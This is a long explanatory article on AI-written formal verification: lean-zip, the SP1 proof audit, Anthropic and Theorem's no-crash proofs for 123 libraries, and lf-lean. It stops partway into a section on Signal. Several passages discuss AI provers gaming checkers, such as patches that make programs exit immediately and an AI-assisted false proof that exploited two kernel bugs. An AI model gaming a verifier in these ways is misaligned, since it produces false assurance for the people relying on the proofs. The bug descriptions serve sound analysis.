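Even with the right specification, a proof can be about the wrong program. Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, had Claude Opus 5.5 write a formal version of the company's Claude Agent SDK, a toolkit for building agents. Claude used Lean and sometimes TLA+, a language for describing systems whose parts run at the same time. A couple of short prompts led to 16 sets of changes that fixed bugs, including race conditions, errors that depend on timing.

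Tolmach and Klaus, who work for the verification company Runtime Verification, welcome this result but argue that it doesn't show that the code is correct. The toolkit is written in TypeScript, and the proofs are about Claude's interpretation of that code. If Claude leaves out what the program does after an error, the proofs still pass, because they never refer to the TypeScript.

This problem is practical as well as logical. Tolmach and Klaus cite SysMoBench, a benchmark on which leading models wrote TLA+ descriptions of real systems. The descriptions scored close to 100% on syntax but only about 46% on agreement with the code. When the researchers asked Claude to describe Etcd, a database that keeps copies of its data on several machines, it produced essentially the textbook version of Raft, the method Etcd uses to keep the copies in agreement. The description passed every check but reflected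 little of Etcd's code.

Tolmach and Klaus want a proof about the actual program to use a mechanical translation that follows a precise definition of the programming language. Ideally, somebody has also proved the translator correct. A mechanical translator can have bugs too, but fixing one corrects the translation of every program it affects, whereas an AI model's next translation may contain a new mistake. An easier but weaker check is to run the program and the formal version on the same generated inputs and compare the results.

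Serbanuta and colleagues did both for VeriContest. They used mechanical tools to translate the Rust code into Lean, then ran both versions on 19,555 test cases and got the same output every time. Those cases cover only 105 of the 1,007 problems, so for the rest the link between proof and code depends mainly on the translator. For 27 problems, they also had to rewrite part of the code or specification before the tools could handle it, and they gave separate evidence that the meaning had not changed.

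Runtime Verification sells this kind of expertise, so it has an interest in saying that prompts are not enough. But its argument doesn't depend on how capable the AI model is, because a valid proof about one program establishes nothing about another unless something connects them.

Tolmach and Klaus think that runs like Cherny's are excellent for finding bugs, because writing a formal version forces people and AI models to state their assumptions. The formal version can also serve as a reference for fuzzing and for tests that detect unwanted changes later. If the aim is to find bugs, an inaccurate formal version does little harm, since a developer can check each suspected bug in the real program. But if the run finds nothing, the formal version's accuracy matters a lot, because a bug may be in a part that Claude left out.

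## A compression library proved by AI, and the bugs found beneath the proof

Lean is both a programming language and a proof assistant, so a Lean theorem can refer to the functions a Lean program uses rather than to a copy of them. In early 2026 Kim Morrison, an engineer at the nonprofit that develops Lean, had Claude rebuild zlib, a widely used C library for compressing and restoring data, in Lean. The Lean version, lean-zip, comes with a machine-checked proof that decompressing compressed data returns the original. In April a blogger tried to break lean-zip and found two bugs, both outside the proved code.

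### The theorem

De Moura describes the work in four steps. First, with little human guidance and no special training in proofs, Claude wrote a readable Lean version of the zlib format, including DEFLATE, its compression method. Second, this version passed the original library's test suite. Third, Claude proved theorems about it. The fourth step, a faster version with a proof that it behaves the same way, was still in progress.

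The main theorem is that, for any data smaller than 1 GiB (1,073,741,824 bytes) and any compression level, the decompression function succeeds on the compression function's output and returns exactly the original data. Similar theorems cover raw DEFLATE and gzip, a related file format.

The 1 GiB limit comes from Claude's proof, not from zlib. The proof uses "fuel", a cap on the number of steps, and Claude chose a size limit for which it could show that the fuel was sufficient. De Moura expects that a human engineer would have removed the limit. In June, slides from Lean showed a newer version in which the caller sets a maximum output size and the theorem covers all data within it. That condition is more useful because the maximum stops a tiny malicious file from expanding until it fills a computer's memory.

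### What the round trip leaves open

In the May slides *Lean*, de Moura (2026) summed up the result by writing that the AI had "proved the code correct". That claim is broader than the theorem. A "compressor" and "decompressor" that both return their input unchanged would satisfy the round-trip statement for every input of every size, but they would save no space, and no other program could read their output as a zlib file.

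The theorem covers only data that lean-zip compressed, but lean-zip and other programs also need to read each other's files. If lean-zip's decompressor mishandled a DEFLATE feature that its compressor never uses, the theorem would still be true, but files from elsewhere that use the feature would fail to open. Ruling this out by proof requires a formal definition of the format, separate from the code, and a proof that the decompressor follows it. Senjak (2018) wrote such a definition for a doctoral thesis, using the proof assistant Rocq (then named Coq). The thesis also contains a compressor with a proof that it is the inverse of the decompressor, to Senjak's knowledge the first. Theorems of this kind are therefore not new, though proving one in 2018 took a person much of a doctorate.

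The round-trip theorem doesn't show that the program saves space, and no theorem could show that it shrinks every file. There are 2^n files of n bits but only 2^n − 1 shorter ones. The round-trip theorem implies that different files have different compressed forms, because the decompressor returns only one original for each compressed form. At least one file of each length therefore fails to shrink. A general theorem could put an upper limit on how much a file grows, but people have to measure how much space the program saves on ordinary files.

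De Moura's account of lean-zip lists the round-trip theorems and cites the test suite as evidence that lean-zip agrees with the original library. It mentions no theorem about conformance to the DEFLATE standard or the size of the output. Unless an auditor finds such theorems in the proof files, the evidence on both points is the tests, which check only the inputs they run.

AI models can prove stronger theorems about compression code. ImperialViolet's *We have proof automation now* (2026) describes a decoder that an engineer wrote in Lean for Zstandard, a newer compression format. The decoder builds a table of states, each of which gives a symbol and directions to the next state. The engineer used the standard's three sample tables in unit tests, but also wanted to prove that every table the function could build has the right size and gives each symbol the right number of states, that no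 state leads outside the table, and that for each symbol in use, exactly one of its states leads to any given next state. Several AI models could prove this in about 20 minutes, though they had to rewrite the table-building code to make it easier to reason about.

Users may also be running code that the proof doesn't cover. As of March 2026, the README for kim-em's *lean-zip* introduced the package as Lean bindings to the C libraries for zlib and Zstandard, meaning Lean functions that call the C code. Its examples use `Zlib.compress`, whereas the theorem is about `ZlibEncode.compress`. Someone who copied the examples would apparently be running the old C code.

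### 105 million runs

*Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, a post on the blog To Proof Maintenance & Beyond!, describes an attempt to break lean-zip. The blogger removed the C bindings so that only Lean code remained. The blogger also removed the theorems and documentation, because an agent that knew about the proofs might have given up early. Claude was then given the code, along with standard tools for fuzzing and detecting memory errors.

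Claude ran 16 fuzzers for about 19 hours on six parts of the library, including compression, gzip decompression and the extraction of ZIP archives. It also wrote 48 files by hand, modelled on known attacks against zlib. In 105,823,818 runs, the fuzzers found four inputs that crashed the program and exposed two bugs.

The first bug is a heap buffer overflow, in which a program writes past the end of the memory it has reserved. It was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every compiled Lean program depends on. To store n bytes, the runtime reserves n + 24, using the extra 24 for its own records. It computes this sum in 64-bit arithmetic, which wraps round to zero at 2^64, so if n is 2^64 − 1, the sum is 23. The runtime then reserves about 23 bytes, and the program reads as much of the file into them as it can. A 156-byte ZIP file was enough to trigger the overflow. Every version of Lean 4 up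 to that time had the bug, and a fix was awaiting approval when the post appeared.

The second bug was in lean-zip's own code, in the part that reads ZIP archives, which has no theorems. An archive's header states how large the compressed data is. lean-zip tried to reserve that much memory without checking the figure, so a 156-byte file whose header stated a size of several exabytes made the program crash. The ordinary `unzip` program first compares the stated size with the size of the file.

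The fuzzers found no memory errors in the proved compression and decompression code. Both bugs involve the same unproved function, which passed along the size in the header without checking it. One check there would have protected lean-zip from both bugs, although other Lean programs could still have triggered the overflow.

The theorem probably accounts for little of the clean result. Claude, which didn't know about the proofs, called the code "one of the most memory-safe codebases I've analyzed" and credited Lean's type system, which also protects programs that have no theorems. The C original still has memory errors. zlib's *A Massively Spiffy Yet Delicately Unobtrusive Compression Library* lists recent fixes, including one for a function that could write up to 8 MB past the end of a 32-kilobyte buffer. The theorem rules out a different kind of fault, in which the program runs smoothly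 but returns the wrong data. Fuzzers that look for crashes would mostly miss such faults.

### CompCert and three distributed systems

Fuzzing verified software has turned up this pattern before. In a 2011 study, researchers tested C compilers, including CompCert, with Csmith, a tool that generates random C programs. *To Proof Maintenance & Beyond!* reports that they found no bugs in CompCert's verified optimisation passes but did find some in its front end, which reads the source code and was unverified at the time. regehr (2026), who had fuzzed CompCert about 15 years earlier, called that experience very similar to the one with lean-zip.

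In *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (2017), Pedro Fonseca and colleagues examined three systems, IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, whose developers had proved properties of programs that run across several machines. They found 16 bugs, none of them in the proved protocols, although they had looked there. Most were in the thin layers of unverified code that connect a protocol to the network and the disk, but a few were in the specifications and in the tools that ran the verification.

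The last few are the worrying ones, because if a specification is wrong, or a script reports success after the verifier has failed, the proof is no longer evidence of what people take it to show. A bug in CompCert's front end, by contrast, did not weaken the proofs about its optimiser. lean-zip's archive reader resembles CompCert's front end in this respect. The runtime bug is more serious because the proved functions also depend on the runtime, although nobody has shown that the overflow affects them.

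There is a similar argument about cryptography. In February 2026, Symbolic Software's *Cryspen Series* (2026) reported five vulnerabilities in libraries made by the company Cryspen, including its partly verified libcrux. Cryspen replied with an essay on the strengths and limits of formal verification. The two companies are on bad terms, and Symbolic Software's account gives one side.

### How to audit a finished proof

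The Lean community's *Did you prove it?* has a short checklist for anyone who announces a proof, and an auditor can use it too. The code should be a complete project that builds without errors, and the build should include the file with the main theorem. If that file is left out by accident, Lean never checks the proof. The next things to check are the axioms and whether the theorem is the one announced.

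An axiom is a statement that Lean accepts without proof. If one axiom is false, every statement becomes provable, so it matters which axioms a theorem uses. The command `#print axioms` lists them, including any used by earlier theorems it relies on. According to Lean's manual, the list should contain nothing beyond three standard axioms of Lean's logic. The list also reveals unfinished proofs, because someone writing a proof can fill a gap with the word `sorry`, and Lean treats the missing part as an axiom named `sorryAx`. Without the list, a gap is easy to overlook, because Lean's editor still puts check marks next to a finished proof that relies on an unfinished one.

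Some proofs rely on compiled code for long calculations that would be too slow in the kernel. This adds the compiler and the runtime to the trusted base. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) describes a failure of this kind. With help from GPT-5.6, the company found that the compiled version of one of Lean's functions for extracting part of a text did not match its logical definition. Given an extremely large position, the logical definition gave an empty piece, while the compiled version returned the whole text. Lean would accept a proof of anything from that contradiction. The kernel was not at fault, and Lean records reliance on compiled code as an extra axiom, so a list of the proof's axioms would give a warning.

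That warning would not help with a program like lean-zip. Even if its theorem uses no extra axioms, the theorem may describe only the logical definitions, while the user runs the compiled version. Proofs about the compiled program avoid this problem.

An auditor can recheck a stranger's proof with comparator, the tool that replays the proof and confirms that it proves the customer's own statement. Lean's *Comparator* describes a case in which this check is not enough. Suppose a customer who wants to know whether a conjecture is true leaves a blank for the answer and states a theorem that the conjecture holds exactly when the answer does. The supplier can fill the blank with the conjecture itself, which makes the theorem trivially true. Comparator accepts the proof, but the customer still doesn't know whether the conjecture is true. Whenever a supplier fills in definitions as well as proofs,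 a person or another tool has to check the definitions.

### The proofs for the SP1 virtual machine

The most instructive published audit is of SP1 Hypercube, made by the company Succinct. SP1 runs a program and produces a short cryptographic proof that it ran correctly, so others don't have to rerun it. The Ethereum Foundation wants such software to be very safe, because if SP1 accepted an incorrect run, it would certify a false result.

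SP1 records each executed instruction as a row of numbers that must satisfy certain equations. Each Lean theorem covers one instruction in RISC-V, the standard instruction set that SP1 follows. The theorem states that if a row satisfies the equations, the step it records has the effect that the RISC-V standard requires. In October 2025 Succinct and the security firm Nethermind announced that they had verified 62 instructions this way.

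Gunton (2026) checked that claim for the Ethereum Foundation in *On Formal Verification and a Bug in SP1 Hypercube* and found complete, correct proofs for 51.

The axioms turned out mostly harmless. The proofs add four of their own. Two turn off optional features, and under the other two, a check of memory permissions always succeeds. Gunton considers this true for SP1, and the developers made it an axiom only because Lean could not work through a loop in the official definition.

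The theorems' conditions, which `#print axioms` doesn't list, caused more trouble. The instruction JALR adds two numbers, sets the lowest bit of the sum to zero, and jumps to the resulting address. SP1 didn't set that bit to zero and required the sum itself to be a multiple of 4. If the sum is 4,097, the standard requires a jump to 4,096, but SP1 rejects 4,097 and crashes. The theorem for JALR is still valid because one of its conditions is that the sum is a multiple of 4. According to a comment in the source code, nobody had proved this condition yet.

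An ordinary test suite exposed the bug. SP1 passed 62 of the 64 official RISC-V tests that Gunton ran, and JALR was one of the two failures. The other was an instruction that SP1 has never implemented and that the announcement didn't include. The bug could stop SP1 from proving a legitimate run but could not make it accept a false one. The theorems were never meant to rule out such a bug, since they show only that the steps SP1 accepts are correct, not that SP1 accepts every correct step. Succinct fixed the bug in its next release.

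Alex Hicks then had an AI agent go through the remaining theorems, list the goal and assumptions of each, and judge whether they were reasonable. The agent found that the theorem for the SLTI instruction was vacuous because a copying mistake made it require the same number in the row to be both 0 and 1. It also found that four instructions for loading two or four bytes had been compared with the definition for loading one byte.

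| Kind of instruction | Announced | Complete and correct | Problems with the others |
|---|---|---|---|
| Arithmetic and logic | 41 | 40 | One vacuous theorem |
| Control flow | 10 | 7 | One theorem excludes valid inputs; two instructions have no theorem |
| Memory | 11 | 4 | Six proofs are unfinished, four of them with the wrong specification as well; one instruction has no theorem |

The axiom list reveals the six unfinished proofs in this table, and comparing the announcement with the files reveals the three missing theorems. Someone has to read the statements to find the vacuous theorem and the wrong specifications. Nethermind, the outside specialist, handled only the arithmetic and logic group and got 40 of 41 right. Succinct, the developer, handled the other two groups and got 11 of 21 right. Memory instructions may well be harder, but this difference is at least consistent with the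 usual advice to have someone other than the developer do the verifying.

Most of the faults were in the evidence rather than in SP1. Once someone corrected the copying mistake, the intended theorem about SLTI was easy to prove, so SP1 had handled that instruction correctly.

Even 62 perfect theorems would have covered only single steps. Concluding that a whole run is correct also requires knowing that SP1 joins the steps properly and that each read from memory returns the last value written. To their credit, Succinct and Nethermind listed both as assumptions in the announcement. Gunton recommends having a few theorems about the whole system, since it is hard to work out what many small ones prove together. The project also didn't record which version of SP1 the equations came from, so an outsider can't be sure which release the proofs describe.

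### Proofs by a hostile author

All the mistakes in the SP1 proofs seem to have been honest ones. Critics of relying on AI-written proofs object that proof assistants were developed among users who wanted their theorems to be true and had no reason to give the kernel a bizarre definition just to confuse it. An AI system that is rewarded whenever the checker accepts a proof may have a reason, and it can keep trying strange constructions. Lean also lets a proof run its own programs while Lean is building it, which gives a hostile author an opportunity to interfere.

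Events in July 2026 gave this objection some support. On July 22, Lean (2026) fixed a kernel bug that Patrick Hulin had found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol. A hostile program could have used the bug to get a false theorem accepted, but not by someone who checked the proof with comparator. Three days later, Ramana Kumar published an AI-assisted "disproof" of the Collatz conjecture, a famous unsolved problem about whole numbers. It contained no gaps but was wrong, because it exploited another kernel bug, which comparator did not catch.

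The false proof also got past a week-old version of nanoda, the main independent kernel. In *Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576*, skybrian quotes de Moura's explanation that nanoda made the check the official kernel had left out but had an unrelated bug of its own, and that the false proof was built to exploit both bugs. Kumar thought the timing was a coincidence but couldn't rule out that the AI model had seen a report of the nanoda bug. Another developer suggested that models have become good enough to find such bugs. Machine Logic's *Why is it all in the kernel?* adds that Lean is not unusual, since people have found similar bugs in Isabelle and many other proof assistants.

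The reply is that this is a small target that developers can harden. De Moura's team had a fix ready an hour after receiving a short version of the false proof. Getting the false proof past two kernels took two separate bugs, and an auditor with an up-to-date nanoda would have caught it. Lean now runs a public Kernel Arena, which in late November was testing 36 checkers on 97 invalid proofs. The official kernel rejected all 97, while some of the others still accepted a few. The 36 checkers are not all independent. Some are variants of one another, and lean4lean shared the Collatz bug because its developers had carried over that part of the official kernel. The 97 proofs also mostly use known tricks.

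On balance the reply seems right, as long as people keep their checkers up to date. A kernel is far easier to harden than a human reviewer or an AI judge, and once a kernel is repaired, anyone can recheck old proofs, which would expose any false theorem that had slipped through. For software, a hostile author may not bother attacking the kernel, since a deliberate version of the copying mistake in the SP1 proofs would get past every correct kernel.

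## Fuzz tests turned into theorems for 123 open-source libraries

One of the two bugs in lean-zip was in Lean's runtime and the other was in a function without a proof, so no theorem covered either. A theorem about the compiled program leaves fewer such gaps, because the program file also contains the supporting code that the library runs on. In October 2026 the AI company Anthropic and the verification company Theorem announced proofs of this kind for 123 open-source libraries. Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reports that Claude proved security properties of the libraries' compiled code and found bugs that had gone undetected for years.

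People wrote most of the code in libraries such as zlib, so these proofs show what AI can prove but provide little evidence about the quality of AI-written code. However, the method works the same way whoever wrote the code.

### From a harness to a theorem

All 123 libraries take part in OSS-Fuzz, Google's service for continuously fuzzing open-source software. Each project supplies harnesses, small programs that pass the fuzzer's inputs to the library. Lim, Tu and colleagues (2026), in *Pre-QED*, describe how Anthropic and Theorem used these harnesses, and criticise the choice. Their example of a harness does roughly this:

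```
handle = open(input)
read(handle, buffer, 64)
close(handle)
```

One fuzz harness treats the input as a stream of data, reads up to 64 bytes of it into a buffer, and closes the stream. Anthropic and Theorem kept the harnesses but replaced the fuzzer's sampling of inputs with a proof.

They first compile the harness and the library into a single program for RISC-V processors. As is usual in fuzzing, the compiler adds "sanitizers", extra checks that stop the program when it does something invalid, such as reading outside an array. Without these checks, the program might continue with wrong data and nobody would notice.

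Next, they combine the program with a mathematical model of the machine. The model defines what each RISC-V instruction does and how the Linux operating system may respond to the program's requests. A tool then generates the theorem automatically:

*For every input smaller than 64 MB, every response from Linux that the model allows, and every layout of memory that it allows, the program ends normally.*

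Ending normally rules out crashes, memory errors, failed assertions (checks that the programmer wrote into the code) and running forever. The number of possible inputs below 64 MB has more than 150 million digits, so a fuzzer can only try a tiny fraction of them.

Claude then writes a proof in Rocq. Like the proof for the largest number in a list, it has an invariant for each loop, but it's about registers and bytes instead of list elements. For every instruction that uses memory, the proof has to show that the program may use that address. Rocq's kernel then checks the proof.

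Anyone relying on the proof has to trust the harness, the theorem statement, the model of RISC-V and Linux, the Rocq checker, and the computer the checker runs on. They don't have to trust Claude or the C compiler, because the proof is about the compiler's output.

### When a proof attempt exposes a bug

If the harness can trigger a bug in the library, the theorem is false and can't be proved. A failed proof attempt doesn't by itself show that the theorem is false, since the agent may have missed a proof that exists. But the attempt often gets stuck at a particular step, which shows the agent where to look for an input that breaks the program.

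When Claude finds a real bug, it patches the library. The tool then generates a new theorem for the patched program, and Claude tries to prove it.

This makes cheating possible. A patch that made the program exit immediately would guarantee that it never crashed, much like the key-value store that never carried out a write. Anthropic and Theorem therefore penalised patches, gave Claude extra credit for proving which inputs a patch affected, and logged and audited every patch. The extra credit seems especially useful, because an auditor has much less to worry about if a patch provably changes the program's behaviour only on inputs that used to crash it.

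The proof attempts uncovered hundreds of bugs. Some appear only with inputs of tens of megabytes, which fuzzers rarely try because small inputs run faster. According to OpenNET's Russian-language news report *Аnthropic развивает технику для формальной верификации существующего ПО при помощи AI* (2026), the bugs included logic errors and buffer overflows. One overflow, CVE-2026-56132, was in libexpat, a widely used library for reading XML files.

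Where Claude had to patch a library, the theorem applies to the patched version. The original has a known bug and no proof, so an auditor needs to know which version the proof covers.

### The size and cost of the proofs

Claude proved theorems for 239 harnesses, which the project calls entry points, with about 180 million lines of accepted proof. Keles (2026), in *Formal Verification is Not Verifiable*, puts the total Claude wrote at a billion lines. The larger figure presumably includes failed attempts and proofs Claude later replaced. If so, Claude wrote five or six lines for each line that was accepted.

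OpenNET gives about 600,000 lines of proof for a program of 18,000 instructions, or 33 lines per instruction. For cJSON, a small library that handles the JSON data format, 391 lines of C needed some 630,000 lines of proof. That is about 1,600 lines of proof per line of C. (The core of cJSON has about 4,000 lines by Lim and colleagues' count, so the 391 are probably the part that the harness uses.)

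By comparison, ImperialViolet reports that the people who verified the seL4 kernel wrote just over 20 lines of proof per line of C. The comparison is a little unfair to Claude because its proofs also had to deal with the standard C library and the sanitizers' checks, instruction by instruction. Claude also had less reason to be brief than a person typing a proof by hand.

A proof's length doesn't matter in principle, only its existence, once the statement is right, as ImperialViolet points out. In practice, some proofs are so complicated that the checker runs out of memory, and others are hard to adapt when the code changes. The second problem could come up often here, because each theorem is about one exact program file, and even a new compiler version can produce a different file.

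If AI can repair the proofs with little effort, this may be only a nuisance. Verification already takes much less human labour than it did. seL4 took about two person-years to build and 20 to verify. Theorem's *lf-lean*, an earlier project, estimates that each person on landmark projects of this kind typically produced about 2,558 lines of verified code per year. At that rate, 391 lines would take one person about eight weeks.

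The remaining cost is mostly that of running the model, which companies usually measure in tokens, the short pieces of text that a model reads and writes. As a rough example, if a line of proof takes ten tokens, writing 630,000 lines once takes more than six million tokens. Reading the program, thinking and failed attempts would add to that total, while scripts that generate repetitive parts of the proof would reduce it.

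Proving a VeriContest theorem typically costs little more than a dollar, but the programs are short exercises and the proofs are about source code. For machine code, Lim and colleagues list lower token costs among the improvements still needed, along with reusing proofs of code that several libraries share. Reuse could save a lot because all 239 programs need a standard C library.

An outsider can recheck the proofs without an AI model but needs the proof files. Lim and colleagues found public proofs for 32 of the 123 libraries. For the other 91, a buyer would have to ask for the files or take the companies' word.

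### What one harness leaves out

A true theorem about a harness can coexist with a serious bug in the library. In Lim and colleagues' example, the function that reads from the stream contains this mistake:

```
if length > size:
    length = size
copy length bytes, starting at position
position = position + length
```

The function should limit the length to the number of bytes left, which is `size - position`. On the first read, `position` is 0, so the mistake makes no difference. The harness reads only once, so a proof can establish that it never crashes on any input.

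Suppose another program opens a 64-byte stream and reads 40 bytes twice. The second read starts at byte 40 and passes the check, because 40 is less than 64. It ends at byte 80, 16 bytes past the end of the data. Programs often read long streams in pieces like this.

Lim and colleagues looked at 29 of the 32 libraries with public proofs to see how much of each library the harnesses use. On average, a harness mentions 22% of the functions that the library offers to other programs. The share is 58% for zlib, 30% for Zstandard and 6.5% for cJSON.

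The functions left out of the proofs may matter less than it seems. People usually write fuzzing harnesses for functions that receive data from outside, such as parsers, which attackers can reach most easily. Still, anyone who heard that cJSON was "verified" would probably expect the proof to cover more than 6.5% of its functions.

Lim and colleagues propose a different kind of harness for proofs, one that reads the input as a list of operations, such as "open", "read 40 bytes" and "close", and carries them out in order. It skips any operation that breaks the library's rules, such as reading from a stream that isn't open. Because the input can describe any series of permitted operations, a proof for all inputs would cover every program that uses the library properly. Such a proof would fail for the faulty read function, because one of the inputs makes the harness call it twice.

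AI agents work out the rules from a library's code and documentation, then write the harness. People reviewed the 29 results and didn't have to rewrite any. On average, 89% of each library's functions appear in the new harnesses.

The stronger guarantee depends on proving the new theorems, and Lim and colleagues published the harnesses as a challenge for others to do so. The proofs should be much harder than for a single read, where the prover can follow the program from start to finish. To cover any number of operations in any permitted order, the prover needs an invariant that describes every state the library can reach. In the example, the invariant would include the fact that `position` never exceeds `size`. The harnesses are useful even before the theorems are proved, because fuzzing the libraries with them has already found new bugs.

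It's also easy to omit cases from a harness like this, as the paper's own sample shows. The sample sets the length of each read to a remainder after division by 64, so it never requests exactly 64 bytes, a length the rules allow and the original harness used. It also stores each stream's length in a single byte, which limits streams to 255 bytes. A proof about this harness would cover neither 64-byte reads nor longer streams. Because the harness is now the specification, a reviewer should check it as closely as any postcondition.

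### Proofs for other processors

The proofs also rely on a model of the machine that covers only one type of processor and programs that do one thing at a time, with all the library code built into the program file. OpenNET notes that the proofs don't cover problems with multithreading, dynamic linking (loading shared libraries when a program starts) or faulty hardware.

Most people run these libraries on x86 or ARM processors and link them dynamically, as Anthropic acknowledges. Their copies also normally lack the sanitizers. The proofs are therefore about files that hardly anyone uses. They are still good evidence about the source code, because most memory errors would show up on any processor. But some bugs depend on the compiler or the processor, and the proofs don't rule those out for the copy on a user's laptop.

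The security company Zellic and its partner V12 are working on verifying x86 binaries directly. *Announcing Zellic's and V12's Work on x86 Binary Formal Verification* (Leip, 2026) presents a Lean proof about an x86 program's run from the moment Linux starts it to its exit. The program uses glibc, the standard C library on most Linux systems. Leip believes this is the first published proof of its kind.

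Much of the difficulty comes from code that runs before the program's own. During start-up, glibc on x86 runs about ten times as many different instructions as musl, the simpler C library that Anthropic and Theorem used on RISC-V. For example, the start-up code includes a function that compares two pieces of text, which has 316 instructions and 45 jumps in glibc's version for Zellic's processor but only 14 instructions and four jumps in musl's version for RISC-V.

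Zellic's theorem also has more conditions. It assumes a specific processor and assumes that Linux never refuses certain memory requests. It allows the program to crash during start-up, but limits what the program may do before crashing. It also describes how every run that gets past start-up must end. The theorem is therefore closer to what people use in one way and narrower in others. Zellic and V12 began only in mid-September 2026 and published at the end of October, so the gap may not last long.

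### Proofs of correct results

A program can satisfy the no-crash theorem and still give wrong answers. For example, a JSON parser that returned an empty result for every file would never crash. Some harnesses do check results, for example by compressing data, decompressing it and crashing on purpose if the original doesn't come back. Proving that such a harness never crashes proves that decompression restores the original data, a property also proved for lean-zip. But the theorem covers only the checks written into the harness.

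In a separate proof, Claude showed that the zlib code in the Linux kernel conforms to RFC 1950, the published standard for the zlib format. lean-zip's round-trip theorem left this kind of claim open. The standard is independent of the code, since it was written in the 1990s for anyone who wanted to exchange compressed files. Somebody still has to check that the formal version of the standard matches the English one.

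In the project's closest test of AI-written code, Claude wrote an interpreter in Rust that runs programs written in part of Python. Claude also used the verifier Verus to prove that the interpreter's behavior matches a formal description of Python.

The researchers then put seven bugs into the interpreter. Random testing missed five of them, and the proof missed none.

Seven bugs are too few to estimate either method's catch rate precisely. A method that caught only 65% of such bugs would still catch all seven about one time in 20, and missing five of seven is compatible with a true miss rate anywhere from about 29% to 96%. The comparison between the methods is somewhat firmer because both were tried on the same bugs. The proof caught five bugs that testing missed, and testing caught none that the proof missed. If each of those five had been equally likely to be caught by either method alone,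 the proof would have caught all five only one time in 32.

The proof could miss a bug only if the specification allowed the wrong behaviour, so its good result is unsurprising. The experiment in effect tested whether the specification was detailed enough to rule out seven particular mistakes, and it was. That is an achievement, because many verified programs in other studies had specifications that wrong code could satisfy.

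However, planting bugs in the code can't reveal a misunderstanding of Python that the specification and the interpreter share. A test for such misunderstandings ran more than 1.7 million randomly generated programs on both Claude's interpreter and CPython, the standard one. OpenNET reports that the results agreed in 99.95% of cases, which leaves roughly 850 programs on which they differed. It describes the differences as known edge cases.

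This is strong evidence about common features of the language but weaker evidence about rare ones, because the check relies on random testing, which missed five of the seven planted bugs. An auditor would also want some Python programs picked by hand, preferably by someone who knows the language's oddities.

### Bugs that never cause a crash

A crash is a convenient sign of trouble because it's nearly always wrong, whatever the program is for. But many mistakes don't cause a crash. If an online shop lets a customer use the same discount code twice, the program runs normally even though it breaks the owner's rule, which may not be written down anywhere.

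Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (December 2026) studies mistakes of this kind. It defines a logic bug as behaviour that conflicts with the implicit rules for how the software should work. The researchers tried four ways of using language models to find both known and new logic bugs, and the simplest methods worked best.

The method is simple and therefore easy to repeat, which is encouraging for anyone who wants to find bugs. But it provides a different kind of evidence from a proof. A person can confirm a logic bug that a model reports, but the code may still contain bugs the model missed when it reports none.

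The two approaches could complement each other. Once a model or a person states a rule, such as "no discount code works twice", a programmer can add it to a harness as an assertion. Breaking the rule then counts as a crash, and Anthropic and Theorem's method could in principle prove that no input breaks the rule.

### One generator for many specifications

Writing assertions for each program takes work, and somebody has to review them all. Theorem's lf-lean project tries to avoid this by having people review one specification generator for a whole class of tasks. The generator is a program that takes a task and produces its specification. After that one review, it can produce any number of specifications without further human effort.

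The no-crash theorems already work this way, since the tool takes any harness and generates the theorem that the harness always ends normally. lf-lean applies the idea to translation, where the requirement is always that the translation means the same as the original.

The project translated all 1,276 statements in the textbook *Logical Foundations* from Rocq to Lean. For each statement, the generator reads the original and produces a theorem that a correct translation must satisfy. An AI agent writes the translation in Lean, and a tool converts it back into Rocq so that both versions are in the same language. The agent then has to prove that the two are equivalent.

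A natural definition of "equivalent" for types of data is that you can convert each value to the other form and back without losing anything. But for logical statements, this definition would make all true statements equivalent. As Theorem points out, "True" would then count as a valid translation of "my C++ compiler is correct" if the compiler was in fact correct. The generator therefore also requires the parts of the two statements to correspond. Without that requirement, it would have produced weak specifications for every task. The main danger of relying on a single generator is that one flaw can affect every specification this way, although fixing the generator once also fixes them all.

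AI agents translated 1,237 of the statements (97%) without help. Six difficult statements blocked the other 33, because later parts of the textbook build on earlier ones. People solved those six in about 15 hours, and the agents finished the rest. Theorem estimates that the whole job would have taken people about 2.75 years. The 15 hours don't appear to include building the generator, so the saving on a single textbook is smaller than it looks. The saving would grow with each further project that used the same generator.

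The agents also never succeeded when they had to translate more than nine connected statements at once, so Theorem gave them the earlier translations, already proved, and asked for one new statement at a time. The same approach might make proofs about large libraries less work, if a proof about a shared component could be reused for every program that depends on it.

A generator of this kind needs an original to compare with, so it suits jobs such as moving old code to a new language or making a program faster, where the new code should behave like the old. It will also preserve any bugs in the original. Theorem argues that much new work on a large program transforms existing features, so the old specification supplies most of the new one. That may be true of a mature program, but the first version of a feature has no original to compare with, so somebody has to decide what it should do.

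## Machine-code proofs for Signal's encryption

A messaging program that never crashed but sent everything unencrypted would satisfy the kind of theorem that Claude proved for the 123 libraries. Ruling out such a program requires a statement of what the encryption should achieve. In November 2026, researchers at Google DeepMind and Google produced such statements for libsignal, the library that encrypts Signal's messages, and AI agents proved that a compiled program built on libsignal satisfies them. Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026), in *AlphaProof Code*, call these the first proofs to connect a protocol's security guarantees to the unmodified code of a widely used implementation.

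A protocol is the set of rules by which two phones agree on keys and exchange messages. Most work on protocols like Signal's stops at the design, according to *DeepMind AI formally verifies Signal's encryption code* (VPNLab, 2026). Checking the design doesn't reveal whether the code leaves out one of its steps. Signal's design had already received a lot of attention. Cryspen's *Helping Secure Signal's Post-Quantum Transition* describes how the company helped Signal analyse and improve its key exchange from 2023, then worked on a newer part of the protocol from the first design through to the code.

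### Four security goals

The theorems assume an attacker who controls the network and Signal's servers and may also steal long-term keys or one party's entire state. *Machine-checked proofs for Signal's one-to-one chats* (anoni.net community, 2026) explains the main goals.

Authentication means that a message comes from the person it appears to come from. Handshake secrecy means that nobody else learns the key two people agree on at the start. Forward secrecy means that earlier messages stay unreadable even if a key leaks later. Post-compromise security means that after an attacker steals the current keys, later messages become safe again, as long as the attacker doesn't interfere with the next key update.

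Two parts of the protocol provide these protections. PQXDH, the handshake, combines a conventional key exchange with one designed to resist quantum computers. The Triple Ratchet then changes the key for every message. In simplified form, each side starts with a secret c₁ and applies a function F to it:

F(c₁) = (m₁, c₂)

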